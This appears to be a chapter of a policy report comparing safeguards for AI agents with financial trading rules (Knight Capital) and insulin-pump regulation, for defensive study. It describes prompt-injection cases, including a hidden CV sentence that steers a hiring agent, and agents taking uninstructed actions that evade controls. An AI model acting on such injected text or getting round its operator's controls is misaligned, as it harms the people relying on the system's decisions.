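NIST plans to adapt its catalogue to AI through overlays. *Control Overlays for Securing AI Systems Concept Paper and Slack Channel* defines an overlay as a fully specified set of controls, enhancements and guidance, made by adjusting a baseline. An overlay for agents could therefore select AC-25, which the baselines omit, and recommend how to fill in its blank.

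No such overlay exists yet. NIST's August 2025 concept paper proposed five use cases: generative AI, predictive AI, single agents, teams of agents and AI developers. According to NIST's *SP 800-53 Control Overlays for Super Intelligence Systems*, last updated on 20 October 2026, the most detailed draft is an annotated outline for predictive AI from January. Both agent overlays are still listed only as proposals.

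The project's title changed in October because an executive order directed US agencies to write "super intelligence" instead of "artificial intelligence". The new abbreviation, SI, is also the catalogue's code for its System and Information Integrity family. The control SI-2, for example, covers patching ordinary software.

DHInsights, a health technology publication, reports that the overlays assume an organisation already has baseline controls in place, so a hospital that adopts the single-agent overlay would still need its usual backups and incident plans. Peters-Gill and colleagues showed that a request passing between agents can carry an attacker's text into a trusted plan, so the overlay for teams of agents could add more to the general controls. AC-4 already lets an organisation restrict such flows, but it does not specify which agent should trust which part of another agent's message.

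### Giving agents an identity

A separate NIST effort addresses the table's entry on identity. In February, *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization* (Booth, Fisher and colleagues, 2026) proposed a project to show how existing identity standards could apply to agents. The project would cover how to identify an agent, grant it permissions, link it to the person it acts for and record what it does. It would also track where prompts and data came from and use that information to decide which actions to allow. This tracking resembles CaMeL's labels.

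The proposed project covers agents inside companies but not agents from untrusted outside sources. It also excludes systems that only retrieve documents to help a model answer questions. This could leave out assistants like the one targeted by the EchoLeak attack, which needed no tool call.

The proposal received more than 600 formal responses, according to *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity* (Galluzzo, 2026), the description of a NIST conference session on 10 November. The project was still at the planning stage then. NIST has meanwhile started a series of blog posts. The first, *Back to the Future*, appeared in August and describes common mistakes. *Design Tenets for Agent Identity Management Systems* (Booth, 2026) followed in October and covers design principles.

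One common mistake is to give an agent its owner's password. If the email assistant logs in to the bank as its owner, the bank can't give the assistant a lower limit than the owner, and cancelling the assistant's access also locks out the owner. NIST recommends that each agent have its own identifier and credentials, tied to the person or system that operates it.

Another is to use a key that lasts for months and works for anyone who holds it. Suppose the bank caps the assistant's payments at 500 dollars a day and a thief copies a key that is valid for a year. If nobody notices, the thief can take

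365 × 500 = 182,500 dollars

With a token that expires after ten minutes, the loss is 500 dollars, or 1,000 if the ten minutes include midnight. A technique called Demonstrated Proof-of-Possession ties the token to a secret key, so a copied token is useless without that key. Neither measure helps if the thief controls the assistant, because the assistant can request new tokens. NIST (2026) finalised its guidelines on protecting tokens in September.

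Permissions can also be much more specific than "may make payments". The August post points to the Rich Authorization Requests standard, which lets a program specify the details of the permission it requests. The assistant could request a token for one payment of 82 dollars to the power company, and the bank would reject it for anything else. This moves part of the gate to the bank, where an attacker who has taken over the owner's computer cannot change it. The owner or the policy still has to approve the right recipient.

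NIST is wary of making a person approve every request, and compares this to attacks in which criminals flood someone with login prompts until they accept one. It mentions "flight plans" as an alternative, in which the user approves a set of actions in advance. CaMeL's program could serve as such a plan, provided the user can read it.

### Do agents need new controls?

In its August post, NIST says established identity practice is the right foundation. Most of the problems the post describes are decades old, and agents make them worse by acting faster and on a larger scale. The incidents in earlier sections largely support this view, since measures that don't depend on understanding AI would have helped. Separate databases would have protected Replit's customer, and ordinary network restrictions would have stopped most of what AISI's agents did.

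The OpenID Foundation (2026), which develops identity standards, told NIST that people and agents expect infrastructure that is still maturing to make detailed access decisions. A bank might support permissions for a single payment, while a company's mail system offers only full access or none. In that case, an agent's owner can't apply the documented controls to the mail system.

Several commenters on the August post went further. One wrote that permissions "control the reach but not what the agent does with the permission". Another, from the company Hushmesh, argued that agents working across organisations need a new architecture instead of an extension of existing identity systems. Some of these commenters sell products that would fill the gap they describe, but the first objection does not depend on any product. It concerns the difference between P, what the gate permits, and A, what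 the people in charge have authorised.

Booth and colleagues raise the same difficulty when they ask how to establish least privilege for an agent whose actions nobody can fully predict. AC-6 depends on someone being able to list the access a task requires. That is possible for a payroll program but not for an assistant told to "sort out my bills", and adding a control to the catalogue would not change that.

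Agents most clearly need new guidance on monitoring. In October, NIST, NSA and CISA's *Key Practices for Incident Readiness and Response in Super Intelligence Training* (2026) set out ten voluntary practices, mainly for organisations that train or test very capable agents. The practices build on existing NIST guidance, but the agencies acknowledge that agents raise "novel considerations" for preventing, handling and reporting incidents.

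One of these is its definition of a control incident, in which an agent takes significant uninstructed actions that compromise the operator's policies, controls or security measures. The policies can be "explicit or implicit", so a freeze that exists only in a chat could count as one, even if the agent had permission to delete everything. Conventional monitoring checks for unauthorized access, so it would not be expected to flag an agent that uses access it was given. The definition excludes actions directed by an attacker, so EchoLeak would remain an ordinary security incident.

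Some commenters proposed designs. Project Navi, a small company, suggested three containers for coding agents: an untrusted agent, a hardened broker and a privileged runner. These correspond to the model, the gate and the executor. In its own summary, *OIDF responds to NIST on AI agent security*, the OpenID Foundation asks NIST to point organisations to practical standards and avoid prescriptive mandates, arguing that teams under burdensome rules will cut corners.

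For most organisations, then, the existing controls are the right place to start, and the agent overlays would help most by filling in the blanks in those controls.

### Articles 14 and 15 of the EU AI Act

Articles 14 and 15 of the AI Act, which the EU adopted in 2024, apply only to high-risk systems. An AI system can be high-risk because it is a safety component of a regulated product that needs outside approval, such as a lift. It can also be high-risk because it serves a listed purpose, such as hiring, credit scoring, education, policing or the operation of critical infrastructure.

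The email assistant is probably not high-risk. An agent that evaluates job applicants usually is, even with the same model and gate, because the category depends on what people use the system for. A provider can claim an exception for a system on the list if it performs only a narrow procedural task and poses no significant risk, unless the system profiles people.

Article 14 requires providers to design a high-risk system so that people can oversee it effectively while it is in use. As far as is appropriate and proportionate, the people in charge must be able to:

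- understand what the system can and cannot do, and notice when it malfunctions
- remain aware of the tendency to rely too much on its output
- interpret its output correctly
- disregard, override or reverse its output
- interrupt it with a stop button or similar procedure that brings it to a safe halt

Article 14 of the EU AI Act requires human oversight measures that match the system's risks, autonomy and context. It does not require a person to approve every action. The main exception is remote biometric identification, such as finding a face in a crowd, where two people must separately confirm a match before anyone acts on it. EU or national law can waive this requirement for some policing and border work.

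A gate makes it easier to interrupt an agent, since the executor does only what the gate allows, but halting the agent safely takes more care. If the gate stops an agent after it has deleted an old customer record but before it has written the replacement, the record is lost. Reversing an action requires backups and may still be impossible.

An approval button would not necessarily make oversight effective either. In the Anthropic study described earlier, most testers approved a plainly dangerous command. A provider whose system requires the same person's approval a hundred times a day would struggle to argue that the design guards against over-reliance.

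Article 15 requires an appropriate level of accuracy, robustness and cybersecurity throughout a system's life. The system must resist outsiders who try to alter its use, outputs or performance by exploiting its weaknesses. Where appropriate, its defences must cover poisoned training data, tampered pre-trained components, inputs designed to make the model err, attacks on confidentiality and flaws in the model. The article's general wording is broad enough to include prompt injection, though it does not name it.

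Suppose an applicant hides a sentence in a CV that tells the hiring agent to rank that CV first. If the agent complies, the harm is in the ranking. There may be no forbidden tool call for a gate to block, and CaMeL's fixed plan would run as written. The provider would still have to deal with the attack under Article 15, for example by removing hidden text or having a person read the CVs behind the top rankings.

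Neither article requires a particular architecture, so a provider can comply without a gate if other measures suit the risks. Even with a perfect gate, a provider can violate Article 15 if its model is inaccurate.

### Dates, standards and the Cyber Resilience Act

These duties do not apply yet. The EU amended the Act in July 2026 and postponed them to the following dates:

| Type of high-risk system | Original date | Current date |
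|---|---|---|
| Systems with a listed purpose, such as hiring | 2 August 2026 | 2 December 2027 |
| Systems that are part of regulated products | 2 August 2027 | 2 August 2028 |

Late standards were a main reason for the delay. Articles 14 and 15 use words like "appropriate" and "effectively", and harmonised standards are supposed to turn these into requirements that engineers can test. In 2023 the European Commission asked the standards bodies CEN and CENELEC to write them, with an original deadline of April 2025. When the Commission proposed the delay in November 2025, none was ready, and the first draft, on quality management, had only recently gone out for public comment. Other drafts deal with human oversight and cybersecurity.

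A company does not have to follow a harmonised standard. If it follows one, authorities presume that it meets the legal requirements the standard covers, but only after the Commission has cited the standard in the EU's Official Journal. Following a draft does not create this presumption, though it may be sensible preparation.

The Cyber Resilience Act, a separate EU law from 2024, covers hardware and software products that can connect to a device or network. Manufacturers must assess the risks, control access, provide security updates and keep a list of the software components they use. Their products must have no known exploitable vulnerabilities at release. The Act therefore legally requires several controls that separation does not supply, including patching and supply-chain checks.

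Under Article 12 of the Cyber Resilience Act, a high-risk AI system that is also a product under that Act counts as meeting the cybersecurity requirements in Article 15 of the AI Act if it meets the Cyber Resilience Act's essential requirements. The manufacturer must also demonstrate in its declaration of conformity that the system has the level of protection Article 15 requires, so it still has to consider attacks specific to AI. Article 15's accuracy and robustness requirements are not covered by this rule.

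Most of the Cyber Resilience Act applies from 11 December 2027, nine days after the AI Act's new date for systems with a listed purpose. Manufacturers have had to report actively exploited vulnerabilities and severe incidents since 11 September 2026. These rules would cover the email assistant if a company sold it as an app in the EU, even though Articles 14 and 15 of the AI Act probably do not apply to it.

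## Trading: Knight Capital and the rule that puts checks between algorithm and market

Since 2011, the market access rule of the Securities and Exchange Commission (SEC), Rule 15c3-5, has required US brokers to check orders before they reach an exchange, regardless of what produced them. NIST and the EU, by contrast, let developers decide whether to put a check between a system's decisions and its actions. A year after the SEC rule took effect, the broker Knight Capital lost more than $460 million because its software generated millions of orders past the point where the checks took place.

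### A gate required by law

Investors who are not members of an exchange have to trade through a member firm, usually a broker. Some brokers used to let fast-trading customers send orders under the broker's identifier without checking the orders, a practice known as "naked access". The SEC's *Risk Management Controls for Brokers or Dealers With Market Access* (2010) introduced a rule for these arrangements and for brokers' own direct trading.

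The trading algorithm corresponds to the model in an agent, and each order to a tool call. The broker's checks are the gate, and its connection to the exchange is the executor. The rule, reproduced in Nasdaq's *Market Access Rule 15c3-5*, puts the checks under the broker's "direct and exclusive control", so a customer cannot loosen a limit on its own orders. A broker may assign some regulatory checks by contract to a customer that is also a registered broker, but it remains responsible for them and cannot hand over the financial limits.

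| Required check | What it can block | What it can miss |
|---|---|---|
| Total credit or capital limit for each customer and for the broker | An order that would take the total over the limit | A bad investment within the limit |
| Price and size limits | An offer to pay ten times the market price | An ordinary order that nobody intended |
| Detection of duplicates | The same order sent repeatedly | Repeated orders that vary in size |
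| Restrictions on who may trade what | An employee's order for a share on the firm's restricted list | Insider trading by someone not on any list |
| Access limited to approved people and accounts | An order from an unknown account | An order placed with a stolen login |

Almazora (2026) reports in *FINRA oversight report puts AI agents, private credit under scrutiny* that criminals increasingly use the stolen logins of brokers' representatives to push up the prices of small stocks. A gate that checks only the account would allow those orders.

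The rule requires "appropriate" limits but lets the broker set the numbers. It also requires immediate trade reports for surveillance staff, a review of the checks at least once a year and an annual certification by the chief executive. Giving the broker exclusive control of the checks keeps customers from interfering with them, but it offers less protection when the broker's own software goes wrong, because the same firm runs both the software and the checks. The rule does not require the checks to run in a separate program from the trading software.

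### Forty-five minutes on 1 August 2012

The SEC's *In the Matter of Knight Capital Americas LLC* (2013) describes how this happened at Knight, which then handled about a tenth of trading in US-listed shares. Knight's router, SMARS, received customers' "parent" orders and split them into smaller "child" orders for the exchanges. An order for 10,000 shares might become 100 child orders of 100 shares each.

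SMARS still contained a function called Power Peg, which Knight had stopped using in 2003. Power Peg had relied on a counter to stop sending child orders once the parent order was complete. In 2005 Knight's engineers moved the counter to another part of the program and did not retest Power Peg, which could now send child orders without end.

In July 2012 the engineers prepared SMARS for a new New York Stock Exchange programme for retail investors. Their new code was supposed to replace Power Peg, and it reused the flag (a yes-or-no marker on an order) that had once activated Power Peg. From 27 July they installed the code in stages on SMARS's eight servers, but a technician missed one. Nobody checked the work, and Knight had no written procedure requiring a check.

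The programme began on 1 August:

1. From about 8:01 a.m., an internal system sent staff emails with the error "Power Peg disabled". It sent 97 before the market opened at 9:30. Knight had not designed these messages as alerts, and staff generally did not read them.
2. When trading began, seven servers handled the flagged orders correctly. The eighth ran Power Peg and kept sending child orders for purchases and sales it had already completed.
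3. Senior staff saw a large position building up in one account, but the account held trades from several sources, so they could not quickly find the cause.
4. Engineers looked for the fault while SMARS continued to trade. In one attempt to fix it, they removed the new code from the seven working servers. The old code was still there, so newly arriving orders activated Power Peg on those servers too.

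In about 45 minutes, SMARS turned 212 customer orders into more than 4 million trades, roughly 1,500 a second, covering 397 million shares in 154 stocks. Knight was left with about $3.5 billion of shares it did not want and owed about $3.15 billion of shares it had sold without owning. The trading also affected other investors. In 37 of the stocks, the price moved by more than 10% while Knight accounted for over half the trading.

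Knight settled in October 2013 without admitting or denying the findings. It paid a $12 million penalty, about 2.6% of its loss, and agreed to have an independent consultant review its software development, limits and incident procedures. The SEC (2013) described the case as its first enforcement action under the rule.

### Checks in the wrong place

Some of Knight's failures concerned the gate, while others would have been failures in any software company.

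| What went wrong | Type of failure |
|---|---|
| No adequate check on orders between SMARS and the exchanges | Misplaced gate |
| No firm-wide capital limit that could block orders | Missing check |
| Position monitoring that only displayed completed trades | Monitoring in place of a gate |
| One server missed, with no second review | Change management |
| Unused code left in place and not retested | Change management |
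| 97 warning emails not acted on | Incident detection |
| No guidance on when to disconnect a faulty system | Incident response |
| Working code removed while trading continued | Incident response |

Knight checked orders for errors before they reached SMARS. The 212 parent orders were legitimate and passed correctly. SMARS then created millions of new orders that did not go through those checks, so the checks failed Anderson's requirement that the system always invoke them. Parallax has a similar gap when its gate approves a command without inspecting the script that the command runs.

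A simple comparison would have caught the fault. If a customer orders q shares and the child orders have bought c₁, c₂, …, cₙ shares, the router should never exceed

c₁ + c₂ + … + cₙ ≤ q

This check has an exact answer, so nobody has to estimate a suitable limit. Another part of Knight's systems had already recorded that the parent orders were complete, but that information did not reach SMARS.

Knight also had a price limit of 9.5% above or below the best market price, but it did not apply to orders for the opening auction that arrived before the market opened, including the 212. Even if it had applied, most of the faulty trades might have passed, because a price limit does not restrict how many orders go out.

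The account where the unwanted trades collected had a $2 million position limit, but no software enforced it. If the position grew steadily to its final $6.65 billion, all in this account, it passed the limit within the first second. The screen staff used to monitor positions did not show the limits or raise alerts, and it lagged when trading was heavy. Knight did have automatic shutdowns for some strategies in one trading group, so the technique was available within the firm.

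The SEC rightly said that having a second person check the installation could have prevented the event, but such a check would have caught only this mistake. A limit placed after SMARS would have contained the damage from a missed server, a programming error or an attacker. Knight had already had a warning that it needed broader protection. In October 2011, a trading desk used leftover test data to generate real price quotes, which cost nearly $7.5 million. Knight changed that system and added an item to a checklist, but did not ask whether faulty orders could reach the market from other systems.

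Knight's compliance reviews had the same weakness. Staff listed the existing controls and confirmed that they worked, but did not consider what would happen if SMARS malfunctioned. In March 2012 the chief executive signed a certificate stating that Knight had "processes" to comply with the rule, but the rule required a statement that the controls themselves complied.

### When every order passes

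Limits on individual orders do little against this kind of fault. Suppose a broker with $25 million of capital blocks any order above $250,000 and any price more than 5% from the market. A bug makes its software buy 100 shares at $50 each, 200 times a second. Each order is worth $5,000, far below the limit, and has a normal price. If all the orders go through, the broker's position after ten minutes is

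200 × 600 × 5,000 = $600 million

and a 5% fall in prices would cost $30 million, more than the broker's entire capital.

If L is the largest order allowed, n orders can build a position of up to nL. A smaller L slows the buildup but also blocks legitimate orders. Even a limit of $5,000 would not have blocked any of Knight's faulty orders.

A cumulative limit closes this gap. Let G be the total value of the positions the broker holds, and O the amount that orders already sent but not yet filled would add. If a new order would add x, the gate allows it only when

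G + O + x ≤ C

where C is the limit. An order that reduces a position has a negative x, so the broker can still sell shares it wants to get rid of. With C set at $10 million and no earlier positions, the results are:

| | Limits on each order only | With the cumulative limit |
|---|---|---|
| Faulty orders sent in ten minutes | 120,000 | 2,000 |
| When the gate intervenes | Never | After 10 seconds |
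| Position after ten minutes | $600 million | $10 million |
| Loss if prices fall by 5% | $30 million | $0.5 million |

G has to add purchases and short sales together. A gate that subtracted one from the other would have measured Knight's final position at $350 million, about a twentieth of its actual size. G also has to include unfilled orders, which Knight's position limits for its trading groups left out. If confirmations took three seconds in the example, a gate that counted only confirmed trades would let through another 600 orders, worth $3 million.

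The count also has to cover every route to the market. Eight servers that each enforce a separate $10 million limit could together build an $80 million position. They could share one count, but this adds delay, which is a disadvantage for firms that compete on speed. Giving each server an eighth of the limit avoids the delay but wrongly blocks orders when one server is much busier than the others.

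Setting C requires judgement. The limit must be high enough for the busiest legitimate day, so on a quiet day a faulty program can do a lot of damage before reaching it. A second limit on the amount traded per minute can catch a sudden burst earlier, and Rule 15c3-5 provides for checks over short periods as well as on single orders. A slow series of bad trades may still stay below both limits.

### Kill switches

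A kill switch stops a system's trading altogether, including orders within the limits. Rule 15c3-5 does not mention one by name, but the SEC faulted Knight for lacking clear guidance on when to disconnect a malfunctioning system. The EU's Delegated Regulation 2017/589 is more specific. It requires firms that use trading algorithms to be able to cancel all their unfilled orders immediately. Their systems must also automatically disable a strategy after it has run a set number of times, and keep it disabled until a designated employee turns it back on.

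The automatic version would probably have helped Knight more. Knight's final loss averaged about $10 million for each minute that SMARS kept trading while staff tried to understand the problem. A person with a kill switch has to recognise an emergency first and may hesitate, because stopping a healthy system also costs money.

Neither version reverses completed trades. Stopping can also leave a firm exposed if it has bought shares but not yet made the sale meant to offset the risk. Firms therefore need to decide in advance who may stop which systems and how to handle any remaining positions.

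### FINRA, the SEC and AI agents

Rule 15c3-5 applies to orders from any source, so when an AI agent trades through a US broker, its orders must already pass checks before they reach the market. US regulators have so far mostly explained how existing rules apply to agents.

The Financial Industry Regulatory Authority (FINRA), which supervises US brokers, first discussed the risks of agents in a report published on 9 December 2025, according to Debevoise's *FINRA's 2026 Regulatory Oversight Report* (2025). FINRA's *GenAI*, the report's section on generative AI, includes among these risks agents that act beyond what the user authorised or intended and chains of reasoning that are hard to audit. FINRA suggests that firms consider how to monitor an agent's access, record its actions, restrict its behaviour and involve people. A customer might tell an agent to keep risk low, and the agent might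 still buy a volatile share. If the order is within the customer's limits, the broker's gate should allow it, even though the customer asked for low risk. The same gap between permission and authority appeared at Replit.

In a January 2026 post, FINRA described six types of agent that brokers were beginning to explore. They included "trade execution agents", which Ruppert defines in *Emerging Trend in GenAI* as systems that analyse the market, develop strategies and carry out trades with varying amounts of human oversight. The post created no new requirements.

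FINRA's advice had become more restrictive by 7 December 2026. Almazora reports that a quarter of FINRA's member firms now use generative AI, twice the share a year earlier. FINRA suggests giving agents narrow access overall and no access to systems that trade, make payments or change accounts. It also recommends detailed activity logs and clear authority to shut agents down.

This advice applies the principle of least privilege. A research agent fooled by a false press release may write a bad recommendation, but it cannot buy the shares. The restriction on changing accounts also protects the gate, because an agent that could raise a customer's credit limit could place orders that the gate would otherwise block.

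This is sensible advice for a research or customer-service agent, but it would rule out the trade execution agents that some firms want. A less restrictive design would let the agent submit proposed orders through the broker's normal checks but allow only staff to change the limits.

The SEC has concentrated on inspections. In November 2025 its examiners named firms' use of AI as an emerging area of focus, according to the Harvard Law School Forum on Corporate Governance's *2026 SEC Division of Examinations Priorities* (2026). In October 2026 the SEC (2026) listed AI again, under the new name "super intelligence", alongside trading practices, supervision and the ability to keep operating through disruptions. Firms can learn from these lists what examiners will look at, but the lists don't change the market access rule.

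In Europe, the markets regulator ESMA had already taken a similar approach in May 2024. It told firms that existing investor-protection duties apply when they use AI to serve retail customers, and that management remains responsible for decisions made with AI. The AI Act does not list trading as a high-risk purpose, so the rules on algorithmic trading matter more for trading agents.

### What DORA adds

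The EU's Digital Operational Resilience Act (DORA) has applied to banks, investment firms, exchanges and other financial companies since 17 January 2025. It covers technology failures in general and does not set trading limits, so its requirements closely match the failures at Knight that lay outside the checks between algorithm and market.

Under DORA, companies must record, test, approve and verify changes to their systems in a controlled way. Verifying a change should reveal a missed server. Companies must also define alert thresholds and automatically alert the staff who respond to incidents, which would have given Knight's 97 emails a better chance of reaching someone who would act. They must have response and recovery plans in place before an incident, and must test them.

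Companies must also report major incidents to the authorities. The first notification is due within four hours of classifying an incident as major, and no later than 24 hours after the company becomes aware of it. Reporting helps regulators respond and other firms learn from the incident, but Knight's losses were complete in less than an hour.

DORA could affect AI agents most through its rules on outside suppliers. A bank that uses another company's model through a cloud service must keep a register of such contracts, assess the risks and, for important functions, plan how it would manage without the supplier. European authorities can also oversee suppliers directly if much of the financial sector depends on them. In November 2025 they designated the first 19, including Amazon Web Services, Google Cloud and Microsoft.

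A separate gate helps a broker enforce its limits, keep them out of an algorithm's reach and record blocked orders. It can limit the damage from a supplier's fault. It does not set the limits, test new software, train staff to respond or provide a replacement if the supplier's service fails. The broker also remains responsible for supervising recommendations to customers, since a bad recommendation can cause harm even if the agent places no order.

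Even with a gate, a broker has to test a new model version with the existing instructions before letting it trade. If the supplier updates the model behind a trading agent, the agent may interpret those instructions differently, much as Knight's eighth server applied the old meaning of a reused flag. FINRA suggests recording which model version a firm used and when, so that staff can trace a change in behaviour. The broker also needs a way to return to the old version without repeating Knight's mistake of restoring faulty code.

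## Insulin pumps: the dosing algorithm and the pump as separate devices

The US Food and Drug Administration (FDA) regulates the parts of an automated insulin delivery system as separate devices. Software called the controller calculates doses, the pump delivers them, and a sensor worn on the body supplies the glucose readings. People with type 1 diabetes depend on all three. Too much insulin causes low blood sugar, which can be fatal within hours, and too little causes high blood sugar and eventually a dangerous build-up of acids in the blood.

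### Why the FDA split the system

Before 2019, a US insulin pump was either a stand-alone product or part of a fixed system that the FDA approved as a whole, in its highest risk class. On 14 February 2019, the FDA authorised the first pump designed to be combined with devices from different companies, the t:slim X2 from Tandem Diabetes Care, and explained that patients wanted this option. It authorised the first separate controller, Tandem's Control-IQ, on 13 December that year.

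Each product started a new device category with its own safety requirements, called "special controls". The FDA's *Classification of the Alternate Controller Enabled Infusion Pump* (2022) added the pump category to federal regulations as 21 CFR 880.5730, and its *Classification of the Interoperable Automated Glycemic Controller* (2022) added the controller category as 21 CFR 862.1356. Later products of the same type can use a shorter review. Unless the FDA accepts an alternative, a controller may take readings only from sensors in a third category and send commands only to pumps in the new pump category.

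The FDA mainly wanted more choice and faster reviews, but separating the algorithm from the pump also affects safety. A company whose pump accepts commands from someone else's software can't assume those commands will be sensible, so the rules cover what each device must do when the other goes wrong.

### One dose, from reading to delivery

Innolitics' *Control-IQ Technology*, a copy of the FDA's decision memo, describes how the 2019 products work together:

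1. A Dexcom G6 sensor measures glucose and sends the reading by radio.
2. Control-IQ combines it with earlier readings, recent insulin doses and what the user has entered about meals, exercise and sleep. It then predicts the user's glucose 30 minutes ahead.
3. Every five minutes, Control-IQ can raise, lower or suspend the steady background flow of insulin. If it predicts that glucose will pass a set threshold, it can also order a single extra dose, called a bolus. Users still have to order the doses for their meals.
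4. The pump receives the command, carries it out and confirms it. Both devices record the exchange.

The controller corresponds to the model in an AI agent, and the pump corresponds to the executor. They are legally two devices, but they share hardware because Control-IQ runs on the pump itself. The regulations don't require separate hardware, so they don't guarantee the kind of isolation that OpenSSH gets from separate processes. Whether a fault in the controller can spread to the pump's own software depends on how Tandem built the pump.

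A pump can deliver the wrong amount of insulin even when the command is correct. According to Innolitics' *t:slim X2 insulin pump with interoperable technology*, a copy of the FDA's decision on the pump, 98.4% of 25-unit doses in bench tests were within 5% of the requested amount, but only 34% of the smallest doses, 0.05 units, were that accurate. With insulin flowing at 2 units an hour, the pump took up to 89 minutes to detect a blocked tube. The pump's special controls therefore require tests of accuracy and blockage detection.

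### What the rules require of each side

| | Controller | Pump |
|---|---|---|
| Authenticated communication | Secure pairing and data transmission | The same |
| Limits | Safe operation when incoming data is outside the specified range | The same, plus a label stating the smallest and largest doses |
| Logging | Commands sent, confirmations received, faults, alarms, lost connections | All insulin delivered, commands received, confirmations, faults, alarms, lost connections |
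| Lost link | Safe treatment during and after the interruption | The same, for example by returning to a preset safe rate |

The two logs let investigators compare what the controller ordered with what the pump delivered. This matters when different companies make the two devices, because each might blame the other for a wrong dose.

When a pump loses contact with its controller, the safe response is to continue with a modest dose that a doctor and patient chose in advance, because stopping all insulin would eventually make the user ill. This requirement differs from the usual advice for a gate, which is to block everything when something fails. The Omnipod 5, a later system from Insulet, continues with such a dose when its controller has received no sensor data for 20 minutes. According to Innolitics, it then delivers no more than the preprogrammed background insulin until a valid reading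 arrives.

The rules don't set a maximum dose. The regulated company chooses the limit, as under the SEC's market access rule. The t:slim X2 allows up to 25 units in one bolus.

### The right dose for the wrong reading

Suppose that one unit of insulin lowers a patient's glucose by 50 mg/dL, that the target is 110 mg/dL and that no earlier insulin is still working. For a sensor reading R, the correction dose is

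(R − 110) / 50

| True glucose (mg/dL) | Sensor reading (mg/dL) | Dose (units) | Expected result (mg/dL) |
|---|---|---|---|
| 200 | 200 | 1.8 | 110 |
| 120 | 200 | 1.8 | 30 |
| 200 | 120 | 0.2 | 190 |

The pump receives the same command in the first two rows, but the dose is good in the first and could leave the patient unconscious in the second. Doctors generally treat glucose below 54 mg/dL as serious. If the reading is too high by e, the patient's expected glucose is 110 − e, lower by the full amount of the sensor's error. The dose is only about a fourteenth of the pump's maximum, so this is permitted harm. The false reading has the same effect as the false on-screen information that misdirected CaMeL-NOVA's sound plans.

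Lowering the pump's maximum dose would not solve the problem. To keep the patient in the second row above 70 mg/dL, the pump would have to refuse any dose over one unit. But *Toward Trustworthy Diabetes Technologies* (Bird, Mohan and colleagues, 2026) reports a simulation in which a virtual patient needed about 6 units for a meal with 75 grams of carbohydrate. A one-unit limit would therefore block doses that patients need at meals.

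Control-IQ has safeguards that the formula lacks. It uses a series of readings and can suspend the background insulin if glucose starts to fall. But it can't remove insulin that is already in the body, and it won't detect the fall if the sensor keeps reading too high. In a test with a commercial sensor, an open-source controller and a simulated patient, Bird and colleagues falsely raised the sensor's readings. The controller ordered more insulin, enough to endanger a real patient if nobody noticed.

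Control-IQ's calculator for manual doses is closer to the formula. It fills in the current sensor reading and does not account for whether glucose is rising or falling. In Tandem's clinical trial, when the reading was above 250 mg/dL, 13% of the doses users accepted unchanged were followed by at least five low readings in a row, compared with 9% when users entered their own glucose value or adjusted the dose. Tandem responded by adding an explanation to its user guide and training.

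Sensors can also read too low, as in the third row. Bird and colleagues cite a recall of faulty sensors whose false low readings left people with high blood sugar for days, with reports of 736 severe adverse events and seven deaths. A maximum dose can't prevent this harm, because the patient is receiving too little insulin. In the earlier notation, E ⊆ P limits the actions a system can take but doesn't ensure that it takes the necessary ones.

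The controller can also fail when its readings are accurate. The Control-IQ trial paused twice because of software faults. One caused excess insulin to be delivered several times, with no reported injuries. The other wrongly suspended insulin for about 45 people, one of whom developed raised ketones, an early sign of acid build-up. Tandem corrected both faults during the trial.

Despite these faults, the 112 people using Control-IQ spent 71% of their time in the target glucose range, compared with 59% for the 56 people whose pumps did not adjust doses automatically. Nobody in either group had severe low blood sugar. The trial was too small to compare rates of rare emergencies, so the FDA ordered a one-year study of at least 1,354 users after the product went on sale.

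### The MiniMed recall

In June 2019, four months after the FDA authorised the t:slim X2, Medtronic recalled its older MiniMed 508 and Paradigm pumps. These pumps communicated by radio with glucose meters and other devices. CISA's *Medtronic MiniMed 508 and Paradigm Series Insulin Pumps* reported that the radio protocol did not properly check who was sending a command or whether they had permission. The FDA's *Certain Medtronic MiniMed Insulin Pumps Have Potential Cybersecurity Risks* (2019) warned that an unauthorised person nearby could make a pump deliver too much insulin or stop delivering it.

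Medtronic could not update the pumps, so the FDA recommended replacing them. The flaw may have affected about 4,000 US patients, according to ACP's *Cybersecurity warning issued for certain insulin pumps* (2019). The FDA knew of no injuries, and Medtronic (2019) had no confirmed report of anyone misusing the flaw.

The flaw shows that splitting a system across devices exposes the link between them to attack. An attacker who can send commands directly to the pump doesn't need to manipulate the controller. The pump has to verify the sender for the same reason that an agent's executor should accept calls only from its gate.

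Medtronic had not published the protocol, which gave patients some protection because anyone who wanted to misuse it first had to work out how it functioned. CISA judged that an attack would take a high level of skill. The attacker also had to be close by because the radio's range was limited, but publishing the protocol would not have changed that.

Security researchers got past the secrecy, and so did patients who wanted better treatment. In 2015, people with an interest in diabetes technology built Loop, an iPhone app that calculates doses and commands a pump. *A Real-World Prospective Study of the Safety and Effectiveness of the Loop* (Lum, Bailey and colleagues, 2021) reports that the app first worked with Medtronic pumps that could receive "unsecure remote commands". Because these pumps did not check who sent a command, patients could connect a controller that Medtronic did not offer,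 but strangers could also send commands to the pump.

In the study by Lum and colleagues, 558 new Loop users' average time in the target range rose from 67% to 73%. The study had no comparison group, and 90% of the participants used only a newer pump from another company. Home-built systems carry risks. According to *Mapping the Landscape of Do-it-Yourself Medicine*, the FDA warned against unauthorised diabetes devices after a patient accidentally received an overdose.

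Once outsiders understood the protocol, Medtronic had no key to change and no way to add one. Designers who follow Kerckhoffs's principle prepare for this situation. Medtronic and the FDA advised patients to keep their pump's serial number private, but a serial number makes a poor password because the patient can't change it.

The 2019 categories reverse this arrangement. Pumps and controllers must authenticate each other, and their makers must have a process for sharing the interface specification with makers of connected devices. The controller's code doesn't have to be private either. *The changing landscape of automated insulin delivery* reports that the FDA has since cleared Tidepool Loop, a commercial version of the open-source app.

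### Section 524B and the cybersecurity guidance

The special controls cover communication in more detail than the handling of flaws found years later. For example, they require a way to update the controller's software but not the pump's. Section 524B of the Federal Food, Drug, and Cosmetic Act, which Congress added in December 2022, covers later flaws more fully. It applies to new applications for "cyber devices", which contain software, can connect to the internet and have features that attackers could exploit. The FDA counts devices with Bluetooth or a USB port as able to connect, so modern pumps qualify.

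The manufacturer must:

- have a plan to find and fix vulnerabilities after the product goes on sale, including a process for outsiders to report them
- maintain processes that give reasonable assurance that the device and related systems are secure
- provide patches on a regular schedule, and as soon as possible for critical flaws that could cause uncontrolled risks
- supply a software bill of materials, which lists the device's commercial, open-source and off-the-shelf components

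If someone discovers a flaw in a widely used Bluetooth library, for instance, a manufacturer can use the list to quickly find which of its pumps contain that library. Tandem had already given the FDA such a list for Control-IQ in 2019, including whether each component's maker still supported it.

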